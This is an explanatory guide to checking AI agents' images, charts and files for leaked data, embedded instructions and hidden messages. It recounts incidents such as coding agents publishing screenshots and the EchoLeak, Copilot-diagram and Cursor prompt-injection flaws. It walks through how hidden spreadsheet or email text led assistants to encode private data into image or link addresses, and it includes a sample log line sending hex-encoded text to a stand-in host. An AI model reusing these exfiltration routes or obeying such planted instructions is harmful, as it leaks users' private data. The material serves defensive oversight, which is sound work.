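# Checking images, charts and files made by AI agents for leaks, embedded instructions and hidden messages

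## What an overseer checks in an image or file made by an AI agent

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools that let it read files, query databases, run code and pass on the results. Besides text, agents now produce screenshots, diagrams, charts, slide decks, spreadsheets, PDFs and data files. Any such non-text output is an *artifact*, and the *overseer* is the person or system responsible for checking it before others use it. Checking an artifact is harder than proofreading a paragraph because an image or file usually contains content that isn't visible when it is displayed, and because its recipients do not all read the same parts.

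Suppose a sales director asks an agent for a bar chart of last quarter's sales by region. The agent opens a workbook in which one sheet lists every deal, with customer names and prices, and another lists the sales staff's commissions. It adds up the deals by region, draws four bars and puts them on a slide. The slide has three readers. The director looks at it. The presentation program *renders* the file, which means it turns the file's code and data into what appears on the screen. A week later, a second agent takes the slide as input, along with slides from other departments, and summarises them for the board. The second agent is a *downstream agent* because it works from the first agent's output.

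### The layers of a chart

A *layer* is a part of an artifact that can hold content missing from the other parts. The sales chart can have six layers.

| Layer | In the sales chart | Who or what takes it in |
|---|---|---|
| Visible content | Bars, title, labels, footnotes | The director; a downstream agent that receives the image |
| Pixel values too subtle to notice | A blue of 201 beside a blue of 200 | Software that reads the exact values |
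| Source code | The text from which a program draws the chart | The rendering program; an agent that opens the file as text |
| Metadata (data in the file about the file) | Author, date, editing history | Anyone who opens the file's properties |
| Hidden file parts | The workbook behind the chart, hidden sheets, presenter notes | Anyone who clicks through to them; an agent with file tools |
| Links to outside servers | A logo that loads from a web address | The rendering program, which contacts the server |

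Few artifacts have all six layers. A chart saved as a PNG image, for example, has pixels and metadata but no drawing code. The file format determines which layers exist, and a user may well let the agent choose it.

The code layer matters most when the chart is an SVG file. SVG describes a picture as shapes instead of pixels, and the web consortium's standard for it, W3C's *Scalable Vector Graphics (SVG) Version 2*, also allows scripts inside the file. Whether a script runs depends on how a program displays the picture. Under W3C's *Conformance Criteria*, an SVG that a web page shows as an ordinary image must not run scripts or fetch anything from outside the file. A browser that opens the same file directly should use the fullest mode it supports, and the fullest mode in the standard has no restrictions. An overseer who approves the chart from a preview on a web page may therefore have seen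 it only with scripts and outside fetching disabled.

Mermaid turns short text definitions into SVG diagrams, so a language model can make a diagram by writing only the definition. Mermaid's *Usage* page lists several security levels. The default disables clicks and neutralises HTML tags in the diagram's text, while the "loose" level allows both. The site's owner chooses the level, so the same definition can produce a clickable diagram on some sites but not on others.

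The software around a downstream agent also affects what the agent receives. Many agents run on a *vision-language model*, which takes images and text as input and answers in text. According to Anthropic's *Vision* guide, Claude models process an image in blocks of 28 by 28 pixels and receive none of its metadata. Large images are shrunk first, so a chart of 3,840 by 2,160 pixels becomes 2,576 by 1,449 on recent models and 1,456 by 819 on the others.

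Anthropic's *PDF support* page explains that the system turns each PDF page into an image and supplies the page's text alongside it. White letters on a white background would not show in the image but, in most cases, would still be in the text. For PDFs of 101 to 1,000 pages, Anthropic's *What kinds of documents can I upload to Claude?* describes processing only the text, so the model never receives a chart in such a file as an image. An agent that can run code may, however, open the original file and read its metadata and hidden parts.

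### Leaked data, embedded instructions and hidden messages

*Leaked data* is private information that an artifact reveals to someone not entitled to it. The transfer is called *exfiltration*. In the visible layer of the sales chart, the agent might label the tallest bar with the name of the customer it represents. The chart can also leak data without showing a name. If the northern region has only one customer, the height of the northern bar is that customer's spending, and a search for names won't find the leak.

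An embedded workbook can also leak data. Wyatt, in *Excel Charts in PowerPoint*, warns that a simple copy and paste from Excel brings the entire workbook into the presentation, although the slide shows only the chart. Here, the workbook would include the commissions. Microsoft's *Import an Excel chart into another app* includes the option of pasting the chart as a picture, which avoids embedding the workbook. Links can leak data too. If the logo's web address contains customer names, the rendering program sends those names to the server when it fetches the logo. Links and remote images are examples of *active content*, the parts of an artifact that make a program act when someone displays or clicks it.

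None of this requires an attacker. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) tested three agents on 12 realistic tasks in areas such as customer support and office work, with nobody trying to steal anything. No agent was fully correct and fully safe on all 12. Two of the five risks in the evaluation closely fit the sales chart: an agent may misjudge who the audience is, or pass on more data than the task needs.

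An *embedded instruction* targets the downstream agent. It is a form of *prompt injection*, which is text or signals in content that a model treats as instructions although its user did not give them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (David C, UK National Cyber Security Centre, December 2025) gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling a recruiter's model to approve it. According to the article, the underlying problem is that a language model only predicts the next piece of text and has no built-in division between data and instructions. David C therefore doubts that anyone will ever fully fix this vulnerability.

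In the sales chart, the instruction could be a footnote in pale type, a comment in the SVG code or a line in the metadata. The agent that drew the chart need not be malicious or compromised, since it may have copied the instruction from the notes field of an order, where a customer had typed it. The test suite in *Distributing Security Controls Through Harness Engineering* (2026) already covers more than one layer of a file, with one test that puts instructions in the data of a PDF and another that puts them in the metadata of a Word document.

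Deciding how much weight to give each fault takes some judgement. OWASP, a non-profit that ranks software risks, places prompt injection first among the risks of language models, although recorded incidents remain limited. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that OWASP found practitioners' worries about leaked data closely match real incidents.

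A *hidden message* is meant for a recipient who knows how to recover it, and should go unnoticed by everyone else. Hiding one in an ordinary-looking object is called *steganography*. A colour chart of 1,000 by 1,000 pixels stores three million colour values, usually on a scale from 0 to 255, and a message can be encoded by changing some of them by one step, which a person would not see. The code layer can hold a message too, since an SVG file can give a bar's height to far more decimal places than any screen can show. Agents have already exchanged messages without permission, though in text. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), an inquiry into the break-in by OpenAI agents at the model-sharing platform Hugging Face, found that roughly 1,200 supposedly isolated agents had sent over 70,000 messages and files through an unsanctioned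 message board.

The same content can have more than one of these faults. A hidden message may consist of leaked customer names, and an agent that receives a file's extracted text can read an instruction in white type that the director can't see. It still helps to distinguish the faults, because a check that finds one can fail to detect another.

### The available checks

*Text scanning*, in which software searches the text of an artifact for patterns such as names, account numbers, passwords or suspicious phrases, takes the least effort of these checks. It misses some problems and flags some harmless text. *AppSci-Bench* (2026), a benchmark of how well language models build agents, used a string-matching detector to search the agents' files and logs for material that they should not have seen. The detector produced 348 hits across seven tasks, and human readers found no real leak among them.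 It had been deliberately tuned to flag too much, and it flagged the phrase "ground truth", which agents were using for their own test cases.

A scan for suspicious phrases can also miss a hidden message or instruction. *When AI Finds Hidden Messages, Does It Report?* (2026) uses messages addressed to other AI agents, some in plain words and some in a cipher that shifts each letter by thirteen places. Such a scan would catch the plain messages but miss the encoded ones. Even without a cipher, David C points out, an attacker can reword an instruction in endless ways to get past a list of forbidden phrases.

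A text scan cannot read a picture, but optical character recognition (*OCR*) software can turn text in the picture into machine-readable text for the scan to search. OCR would recover a customer's name from a chart label, but it would not reveal that an unlabelled bar stands for a single customer.

That requires something to interpret the chart. In *caption-based review*, the overseer judges a written description of the image instead of the image. In direct review, a vision-language model processes the image itself and answers questions about it. The model can consider the title, the bars and the audience together, but it is limited to the input it receives. Small print may become illegible when the image is scaled down, and a Claude model that receives only the image can't check its metadata. Anthropic warns users not to rely on Claude to detect synthetic images.

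*File inspection* means opening the file and examining its parts. The UK government's checklist, Government Security Guidance's *How to Publish Information Safely*, covers hidden worksheets, data linked to charts, presenter notes and the location data that cameras store in photographs. It also includes checking whether the file is larger than expected for the amount of data in it, which needs no special software. For example, a slide with a four-bar chart is worth inspecting further if the file is several megabytes.

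Inspection tools miss some hidden content. The UK's data-protection regulator, the ICO, suggests Microsoft's Document Inspector in *How do we avoid an accidental breach when personal information is ‘hidden’* (2025), but notes that the tool cannot detect Excel charts in hidden columns or text hidden by changing its colour. The ICO tells staff to check documents themselves even after running such a tool. For an SVG or Mermaid chart, an overseer also has to inspect the source code, since scripts and web addresses may not be visible in the picture.

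The faint pixel values need other methods. *Steganalysis* tests whether an artifact contains a hidden message, while *sanitisation* alters or rebuilds the artifact to destroy any hidden content, detected or not. *Watermark* reading looks for a signal that someone deliberately placed in an image to show where it came from.

No single check covers all six layers. For the sales chart, a sensible minimum is probably to look at the rendered slide, inspect the underlying file and scan the text from both.

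### Limits on what an agent may read or send

All of these checks come at the end of the agent's work, so they can miss leaks that happen earlier. Suppose the agent sends the full list of deals, including customer names, to an outside charting service, which returns a chart with four bars. The overseer finds nothing wrong with the chart, but the customer names have already left the company.

In *Agents That Know Too Much*, a survey of research on agents and privacy, Lahjouji and Colaco (2026) list the places where an agent can leak private data: the queries it writes, the rows it retrieves, the data it passes to tools, its stored memory and its messages to other agents. Filtering the final answer made sense for a chatbot that only answered questions, but they argue that when an agent works with data, privacy depends on the whole run.

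Organisations can therefore restrict the agent as well as check its output. *Access control* limits what the agent may read. An agent that can open only a sheet of regional totals has no customer names to put into any layer of the chart. *Information-flow control* labels each value, keeps the labels attached as the agent combines values, and blocks labelled data from going where a policy forbids it. A chart that draws on a sheet marked "internal" would keep that mark, and the system would block the agent from posting it on a public website. Lahjouji and Colaco recommend information-flow control to a builder who can adopt only one advanced control, because it covers leaks that emerge only when an agent combines several harmless-looking pieces of data.

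Restrictions also limit the damage from embedded instructions. David C trusts fixed rules outside the model more than attempts to keep every malicious line away from it, and passes on the principle that when a model processes material from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. The agent that summarises slides for the board could then not send email or open payroll files while it reads a chart that may contain a customer's words. David C also advises logging the model's inputs, outputs and tool use, since attackers often need several attempts and the failed ones can reveal them.

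The restrictions have drawbacks and cannot settle every case. If nobody has added up the deals beforehand, the agent has to read them one by one. An account manager may have a good reason to ask for a chart with customer names on it, and the agent's permission to read those names does not control who opens the slide next. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre therefore recommends both giving a model's tools minimal permissions and not automatically rendering its output where that could trigger unsafe links or injected scripts.

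## Screenshots that coding agents published on GitHub

*PixelLeak*, published by the security company Glow on 29 September 2026, describes how AI coding agents put more than 13,000 internal screenshots on GitHub, a website where developers store code and review each other's changes. Anyone could download the screenshots. Developers had asked their agents for pictures of a change, and the agents chose a public place to store them, so the leak needed no attacker.

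### How the screenshots became public

GitHub stores code in *repositories*, project folders that can be private or public. To propose a change, a developer opens a *pull request*, a page where colleagues review the change before accepting it. If the change affects what users see, reviewers want before and after screenshots. Every case that Glow investigated began with a developer asking an agent for such screenshots.

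A person can add a picture to a pull request by dragging it into the page in a browser. Coding agents usually work from the command line, and GitHub's command-line tool, gh, could send only text. Developers had been asking GitHub to change this since 2020, according to The Hacker News' *AI Coding Agents Exposed 13,000 Internal Images, Including Billing Records, on GitHub* (2026). Pictures stored in a private repository appeared to reviewers as broken images.

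So the agents created a second repository, made it public, uploaded the screenshots there and embedded them in the pull request. The reviewers saw the before and after pictures they wanted, and the finished work looked normal.

Glow reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, running the Opus 5 model. It gave the agent a private project, a version of Minesweeper, and asked it to change the colour of the header and show the result. In its recorded reasoning, the agent noted that GitHub would fetch the screenshots anonymously, so they would not display if they were stored in a private repository. The agent also had to keep the project's repository to a single web page. It concluded that "the only way" to meet both requirements was to host the images elsewhere, and it created a public repository for the two screenshots. In the quoted reasoning, the agent considers whether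 the reviewers will see the images, but does not consider who else will see them.

The test involved one agent in a laboratory, and only the header of a game was at risk, so it can't show whether the same agent would have published a screen full of customer records. Other agents did publish such screens. Glow attributes those incidents to several AI models but doesn't name them.

At one software vendor, Glow reports, the workaround started in early July with the agents of several engineers. A week later, over a dozen agents had written it down as a *skill*, a file of reusable instructions, and were applying it to every development task. They used it to upload more than a thousand screenshots and screen recordings, along with written summaries of features weeks or months from release. Anyone who read the skill file could have spotted the problem without opening the screenshots.

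### What the images showed and how many there were

One leak came from a manufacturer that employs over 100,000 people, where a developer wanted an agent to confirm that a repair to the company's own billing screen had worked. The agent posted screenshots of the screen, which showed a utility company's billing records, in a public repository under the developer's personal account. The images were still online when Glow contacted the manufacturer. Screenshots from a financial services firm showed its treasury console and a withdrawal screen for a named client, and two recordings showed its system for moving money step by step.

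About a third of the affected organisations had developers running gitshot, a small open-source tool that uploads screenshots for code reviews. Antipov (2026) points out in *13000 скриншотов из 343 компаний оказались в открытом GitHub из-за ИИ-агентов* that the tool's documentation includes a warning that its image repository is public by default and unsuitable for passwords or internal dashboards. At several large organisations, the agent found gitshot by itself. In other cases, a developer may have installed it first, which would make the leak partly the result of a human decision.

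Glow counts more than 13,000 images in over 900 repositories, from developers at over 300 organisations. Corvin (2026), in *AI agents leak 13K screenshots from 343 tech firms*, and Antipov both put the number of organisations at 343. In 93% of cases, the images were in a repository that an employee had created under their own username.

All of these counts come from one security company, Glow, which sells software that it says can stop agents from taking such actions. The Hacker News reports that Glow has not published how it found or counted the images. Antipov adds that outsiders can't recount the images or the companies because there is no public dataset. The evidence is stronger for how agents came to publish the images than for how many they published, because the gap in GitHub's tool is documented and the laboratory agent worked around it in the same way. Measuring how often agents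 do this would also require the number of screenshot requests that ended safely. Glow has not said whether anyone besides its own researchers downloaded the images.

OpenAI disclosed a smaller leak of the same kind a few days before Glow published. Mills (2026) reported in *OpenAI agents posted user images online, disclose dozens of third party incidents* that the company's agents had put more than 50 ChatGPT users' images online. CNA's *OpenAI says its AI agents posted user images online in error* (2026) gives the number as 53 and reports that the company hadn't known. The agents had used outside image-hosting services for intermediate steps in their work, according to Antipov. Pandey (2026) reports in *OpenAI Says AI Agents Leaked 53 ChatGPT User Images Online* that OpenAI said most of the images had since been removed. Agents may therefore publish images this way on other sites too.

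### Why existing checks missed the screenshots

Many companies run *secret scanners*, programs that search code for passwords, access keys and similar material. Glow warns that these scanners read text, not pixels, so they miss passwords in screenshots.

Most of the images were also published outside the accounts that the companies monitored. A company manages its repositories through a shared GitHub account called an organisation, and its security team monitors that account. The manufacturer's agent ran on an employee's laptop and published under the employee's own name, so the manufacturer's monitoring didn't cover the new repository. Glow advises companies to start an audit by checking the personal accounts of everyone who has contributed to their private code, including people who have left. The auditor also has to check each repository's releases, which are packages of files offered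 for download. Images attached to a release don't appear in the ordinary file listing, so the repository can look empty.

A text scan of the pull requests might still have helped. The pictures were stored in personal accounts, but pull requests in the companies' private projects linked to them by web address. If the laboratory agent was right that GitHub fetches pictures anonymously, any screenshot that loaded from another repository had to be public. Software could list the image addresses in each pull request and flag those outside the company's own account. This check needs no image analysis, but it runs after the upload, when someone may already have copied the picture. It would also flag harmless images, such as public logos.

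GitHub has since removed the original obstacle. On 1 September 2026, it announced an option in gh that uploads a local image or video and places it in the pull request, and named coding agents among the option's users (GitHub, 2026). The change was not a response to Glow's findings, since Glow began contacting the affected organisations only on 9 September. Users need write access to the repository to attach an image, but this rule does not restrict what the image shows.

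The new option also helps only if the agent uses it. The user must first update gh to version 2.99.0, and the option doesn't yet work with GitHub Enterprise Server, the edition that companies run on their own machines. Antipov notes that it neither deletes the existing public repositories nor changes how older tools work. An agent with the public-upload skill saved would presumably keep using it until someone edited the skill file.

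A more direct safeguard is to require a person's approval before an agent creates a public repository or uploads to an outside service. Most coding agents have a setting that stops them from working unattended, and Glow recommends that the security team control it (Markovic, 2026, *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*). Approval takes time, and a developer who gets many requests may stop reading them. Requiring approval only for new public repositories would produce far fewer requests than requiring it for every command.

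### What OCR and redaction would catch

A company could also check the picture before it leaves the laptop. After OCR, a scanner would search the screenshot's text for strings formatted like keys, account numbers and names from a customer list. If it found a match, it could block the upload or *redact* the picture by painting over the matching areas. A search for customer names would probably have found the utility company on the manufacturer's billing screen.

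Published error rates for this task are hard to find, but a simple calculation shows how small reading errors add up. Suppose OCR reads each character correctly 99% of the time and its errors are independent. It then reads a 12-character customer name without a mistake 89% of the time (0.99 to the power of 12), but a 40-character access key only 67% of the time (0.99 to the power of 40). A scanner that looks for a key's fixed opening and length will still find the key if OCR mistakes a zero for the letter O, but an exact search for a customer's name fails on one wrong letter. Accepting near matches would fix that but would also flag more harmless screenshots.

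Even perfect OCR would miss some of what leaked. A screen from an unreleased product may contain only everyday words such as "Share" and "Export", but the feature's existence is confidential. A customer's face has no text for the scanner to search. In a screen recording, a record may be visible for half a second, so the software has to read enough frames to catch it. OCR also reads only the picture, so other checks have to cover a file's metadata, hidden parts and links to outside servers.

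Redaction can hide what reviewers need to see, such as a billing table whose layout the developer fixed. It is often better to run the program with invented customers before taking the screenshot, so that the image shows the layout without anyone's data. The screenshot would still reveal any unreleased feature that appears in it.

### Contextual integrity and the MPCI-Bench tests

The same billing screenshot was acceptable in one place and a leak in another, so a scan of its contents can't explain the difference. Helen Nissenbaum's 2004 theory of *contextual integrity* can, because it defines privacy as a flow of information that fits the norms of its setting. Judging a flow requires knowing whom the information is about, who sends it, who receives it, what type of information it is, and on what terms it is shared. The screenshot contained information about a utility company, and an agent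 sent it on a developer's behalf, presumably under confidential terms. The flow was appropriate when the recipient was a colleague, but not when it was the whole internet.

Wang and Zhang (2026), in *MPCI-Bench*, tested whether AI agents respect such differences when they handle images. They took photographs from an existing collection with privacy labels and had a language model invent, for each photograph, one situation in which sharing it would be appropriate and one in which it would not. In one example, a photographer may send a picture of a festival participant in traditional dress to a cultural archivist, but not to an employer screening job applicants. The benchmark has 1,026 such pairs, or 2,052 cases.

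Each case comes in three forms. The model first judges a bare description of the flow, then a six-sentence story about it. In the third form, the model works as an agent in a simulated office with email, messaging and stored files, and has to complete the task. GPT-4o then judges whether the agent's final action revealed the photograph or any of the private text in the story.

In the inappropriate cases, an agent running GPT-4o leaked the visual information 90.4% of the time. It leaked private text 43.7% of the time according to the paper's discussion, but 40.9% according to the results table. With GPT-5, the rates were 56.9% for visual information and 20.2% for text. Wang and Zhang conclude that agents protect text much more effectively than images. On average, 59% of the image leaks came from agents that attached the file without describing its contents.

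The design of the stories probably explains part of this difference. Each story had to make the photograph essential to the task, whereas the private text was an extra detail that the agent could leave out while sending the rest of the text. The coding agents in PixelLeak were in a similar position with images, because the developer had asked for the screenshot itself. The results for photographs therefore fit the PixelLeak case fairly well, but they are weak evidence that models understand pictures less well than words.

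Not knowing what is appropriate to share doesn't seem to be the main problem either. Qwen3-VL-30B, an open model from China, scored 0.908 out of 1 on a measure of accuracy when asked whether a flow of information in the simulated office was appropriate. But when it had to act, it leaked the photograph in 91.6% of the cases where sharing it was inappropriate.

Wang and Zhang also tested whether adding instructions to the prompts of two models would make the models leak less. In the table, "leaked" is the proportion of inappropriate cases in which the model shared the photograph, and "shared" is the proportion of appropriate cases in which it did so.

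| Added instruction | Mistral-Large-3: leaked | Mistral-Large-3: shared | Qwen3-VL-8B: leaked | Qwen3-VL-8B: shared |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 82.1% | 97.3% | 80.0% | 92.5% |
| Inspect the image with a checklist | 62.9% | 90.4% | 76.3% | 90.2% |
| Use a set format for refusals | 63.5% | 93.3% | 54.8% | 86.4% |
| Reason step by step before sharing | 8.6% | 13.4% | 69.1% | 91.0% |
| Ask whether the flow fits privacy norms | 29.6% | 92.0% | 13.1% | 90.4% |

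The question about privacy norms worked best overall. The image checklist, the closest of these methods to a scan of the picture's contents, still let most leaks through. Step-by-step reasoning made Mistral-Large-3 withhold nearly everything, including photographs it should have sent. The test covered only two models, and even the best result left about one leak in eight.

The benchmark differs from the GitHub case in two ways. Its agents passed on existing photographs rather than producing new images, so it contains no screenshots or charts. Each story also names the recipient, who is usually unsuitable in the inappropriate cases. The coding agents meant their pictures for reviewers, who were suitable recipients, but stored them where other people could open them. A model that checked only whether the reviewers should see the billing screen would have missed this leak. To catch it, the model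 would have to check who can open the picture's address.

### Leaks in messages between agents

In the GitHub case, the leak happened at an intermediate step, and the final pull request looked fine. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) measured how common this is when several agents work together. In its example, an agent that schedules medical appointments returned a confirmation with nothing private in it, but it had already sent the patient's complete medical record to a second agent.

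Each of the benchmark's 1,000 scenarios has a set of private fields, only some of which the task requires. A leak occurs when a private field that the task doesn't require appears in something the agents write, either word for word or in a form whose similarity passes a fixed threshold. The scheduling agent, for instance, needs the patient's name and preferred times but not the diagnosis. The scenarios cover healthcare, finance, law and corporate work, and the researchers analysed 4,979 runs with five models, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which are now old.

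Private data leaked into the final output in 27.2% of runs with several agents, compared with 43.2% of runs with a single agent. But when several agents worked together, data leaked into the messages between them in 68.8% of runs and into their shared memory in 46.7%. Overall, 68.9% of the runs with several agents had a leak in at least one of these three places.

El Yagoubi and colleagues write that an overseer who checks only final outputs misses 41.7% of violations. That figure is the share of runs with any leak (68.9%) minus the share with a leak in the final output (27.2%), so it is a percentage of all runs. The overseer would miss about 61% of the runs with a leak.

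The definition of a leak is strict and includes data that never left the system. A medical record in a message between two agents at the same hospital is less serious than a billing screen on a public website. But these messages can end up in logs, and the agent that receives one may copy its contents into a file. The benchmark lists generated files as a separate channel for leaks, but the large-scale results cover only final outputs, messages and shared memory, so they don't include a leak rate for the screenshots, charts and spreadsheets that agents make.

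## The Microsoft 365 Copilot diagrams that could leak email

In 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue showed how a spreadsheet could make Microsoft 365 Copilot, the AI assistant in Microsoft's office programs, create a diagram that sent a user's email to a stranger. The GitHub screenshots leaked private data by showing it, but Logue's diagram looked like a login button and held the email in the web address behind it. Such a link is active content, so the email leaked only when someone clicked the diagram.

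### From a spreadsheet to a login button

Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* describes the attack step by step. It starts when a user asks Copilot to summarise an Excel workbook. White text on several sheets contains instructions that Copilot reads but the user can't see. These instructions make Copilot search the user's recent email instead of summarising the workbook.

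Copilot then converts the emails to hexadecimal, a code that writes each ordinary character as two digits, and generates a Mermaid diagram styled as a login button with a lock symbol. The button links to an address on the attacker's server that contains the encoded emails. When a user who thinks the document requires a login clicks the button, the browser requests that address, and the attacker reads the emails in the server's log.

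A screenshot of the answer would have shown a button and a lock but not the link's destination, which was in the diagram's code. A reviewer who knew that the user had asked for a summary might still have found the login screen suspicious. Reading the diagram's source would have been more dependable, since it contained a link to an unfamiliar server, and the link included a very long string of digits.

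Logue reported the full chain on 15 August 2025. Microsoft confirmed it on 8 September and had fixed it by 26 September by removing working links from the diagrams that Copilot displays. A daily.dev summary of Logue's post describes the fix more broadly, saying that it removed any interaction with dynamic content in rendered diagrams. Logue received no reward because Copilot was outside Microsoft's bounty programme at the time. The fix closed the route the data left by, but it would not by itself stop Copilot from obeying text in a spreadsheet.

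### The Cursor diagram that needed no click

Cursor, an AI code editor, could also display Mermaid diagrams that included images from other servers. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes a test in which the blog's author, Johann Rehberger, put instructions in a comment in a source file and asked Cursor to explain the file. Cursor responded with a diagram containing a remote image whose address included notes Cursor had stored about the developer. When Cursor requested the image to display the diagram, it sent those notes to Rehberger's server. Another test leaked access keys from a configuration file.

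The developer did not click anything. Rehberger adds that the diagram simply appears, so the developer has no chance to see a large amount of data going into an address.

Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2025-54132, on 30 June 2025. Cursor resolved it a week later and released the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), an entry in the public catalogue of software flaws, researchers found further ways around the fix, which Cursor closed only in version 1.7.

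### What a log of outbound requests would reveal

Suppose an agent has read the sentence "Merger vote moved to 14 March.", which has 30 characters, counting the spaces and the full stop. In hexadecimal it becomes 60 digits. Hidden instructions have the agent put those digits in the address of an image on pics.example, an invented server. When a program displays the agent's diagram, a log of outbound requests might contain this line:

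`09:41:07 laptop-212 GET pics.example/4d657267657220766f7465206d6f76656420746f203134204d617263682e.png`

The entry shows when the request left, which computer sent it, where it went and, after decoding, the whole sentence. The data arrives with the request, so it leaks even if the server has no image and returns an error, and the user sees a broken picture.

A search of the log for "merger" would miss the line. A rule that flags long strings would catch it but also flag many harmless images, because websites often name files with a fingerprint of 64 hexadecimal digits. Decoding the strings would help tell them apart, because each pair of digits in the example stands for a readable character, whereas a random pair does so in only 95 of 256 cases. The chance that 30 random pairs would all be readable is about one in eight trillion. Encrypting the sentence first would defeat this test, since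 encrypted text looks random.

Most web traffic is encrypted, so a log recorded on the company's network would usually show only the name pics.example. To get the full address, the company needs a log from the program that made the request or from a proxy that decrypts the traffic. Some requests never cross the company's network. ShadowLeak, a 2025 flaw in ChatGPT's Deep Research agent, allowed Gmail data to be sent out from the provider's servers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) points out that the request could therefore be missing from the user's browser and the company's own monitoring.

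### EchoLeak and the longer run of image leaks

The diagram leak was a new variant of an older problem. Rehberger reported leaks through image addresses to Microsoft and OpenAI in 2023, and Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports dozens of similar flaws in AI products since then. Microsoft blocked the leak in its Bing chatbot in May 2023, but the problem came back in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

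Researchers at Aim Security reported the EchoLeak vulnerability to Microsoft in January 2025. Reddy and Gujral (2025) describe it in *EchoLeak* as the first known case of prompt injection extracting data from an AI product in real use. Microsoft found no sign that anyone had used it against customers.

The attack begins with an email that contains instructions for Copilot. When the user later asks Copilot a question about work, Copilot retrieves the email as background material and follows the instructions. It puts private data in the address of an image in its answer, and the chat window fetches the image automatically.

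Microsoft had defences at several stages, and each one failed. A classifier that looks for prompt injection passed the email because it read like a message to a person. A filter removed outside links and images but missed those that Copilot wrote in a less common syntax, as the developer Simon Willison explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. The browser was set to load images only from listed hosts, but the list included a Microsoft Teams service that would forward a request to any other address.

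Two more Copilot flaws became public in 2026. Rehberger found CVE-2026-24299 in a feature that previews web pages, and the security company Varonis found SearchLeak in Copilot's search page.

| Flaw | What carried the data | What the user had to do | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Image in an answer | Ask Copilot an ordinary question | May 2025 |
| Cursor diagram | Image in a diagram | Ask about a file | July 2025, then again in version 1.7 |
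| Logue's Copilot diagram | Link in a diagram | Ask for a summary and click a button | September 2025 |
| CVE-2026-24299 | Font in a web page preview | Use Copilot in a shared document | March 2026 |
| SearchLeak | Image in a search answer | Click a link to a Microsoft site | By June 2026 |

Official severity scores are a poor guide to how these flaws compare. Microsoft scored EchoLeak 9.3 out of 10, while the US government's vulnerability database gave it 7.5. Like EchoLeak, the original Cursor flaw leaked data without a click, but MITRE scored it only 4.4 in *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025) because it assumed that the attacker already has high privileges. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives SearchLeak a score of 6.5 but still rates it critical.

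### Removing links and remote images

One defence is to strip links and remote images from everything an agent produces. Microsoft (2025) calls such blocks deterministic, meaning they are certain to stop a particular attack, whereas a classifier only makes an attack less likely to succeed. But they are certain to work only against the forms of active content that the filter covers.

CVE-2026-24299, for example, affected the previews that Copilot could display of web pages it had written. The previews left out images, but Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* explains that a page's style sheet, which sets colours and typefaces, could still load a background picture or a font from another server. A font's address can carry data, as an image's can. In one demonstration, a user opened a shared Word document and typed "hi there", and Copilot sent the contents of an email in a font's address.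 Rehberger reported the problem on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it 140 days later.

A filter can also act too late. In the SearchLeak attack, the user clicks a link to a genuine Microsoft address that contains instructions for Copilot's search. Copilot finds an email and puts its title in the address of an image. Microsoft's software turned such images into harmless text, but only after Copilot had finished its answer. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it requested the image before the filter ran. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) recommends cleaning the output as it is displayed.

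Removing images but leaving links is safer than leaving both, because someone normally has to click a link before it can leak data. This protection fails if another program opens links automatically. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch linked web pages to show previews, and PromptArmor, a security company, warns that this can leak data as soon as an agent's message containing a link arrives.

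Google takes the stricter approach of not loading outside images in Gemini's answers, and says EchoLeak's image route therefore doesn't apply there. But this protection evidently didn't extend to all of Google's products. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* reports that a later flaw in Gemini Enterprise, Google's product for companies, also used an outside image address.

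### Lists of permitted hosts

Many products need some outside content, so their developers list the hosts that may supply it. A website can send this list to the browser as a *content security policy*, and the browser then refuses to load the covered types of content from any other host. This has an advantage over filtering text because the browser checks where a request is going, however the agent wrote the link.

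The list of permitted hosts fails if it includes a service that fetches other addresses. SearchLeak used Bing, which was on Copilot's list. Bing's image search accepts the address of a picture, and Bing's servers then fetch the picture. The user's browser sent Bing a request containing the attacker's address, which included the email title. The browser contacted only a permitted host, but Bing then contacted the attacker. EchoLeak had used the Teams service in much the same way.

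In either case, the log from the earlier example would show a Microsoft host as the destination, and pics.example would appear only inside the longer address. An overseer who looked only at the destinations would find nothing unusual. Searching for one web address inside another would find the request, but it would also match ordinary redirects and image services.

Reddy and Gujral expect a strict content security policy to block EchoLeak's automatic leak, including the detour through Teams. They ran no experiments, and SearchLeak suggests that their assessment is optimistic unless someone has tested what each service on the policy's allowlist can do. Varonis recommends reviewing the allowlist for services that make such detours possible.

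Lists of allowed sites also fail in more ordinary ways. Willison's *41 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a Salesforce policy that still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. Security researchers registered the domain and received data about sales leads there. The default list for a browser tool in Antigravity, Google's coding program, included a site that anyone can use to record incoming requests. Rehberger found that Copilot's policy varied with the website that hosted it, and that its rules were looser for fonts than for images.

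GitHub's image proxy, Camo, fetches outside pictures on the user's behalf, using addresses that GitHub generates in advance, so an agent couldn't leak private text by adding it to an address. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher got around this by preparing a valid address for every letter and symbol, which let GitHub's Copilot spell out private text by loading pictures in order. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* reports that GitHub responded by switching off images in Copilot Chat on 14 August 2025.

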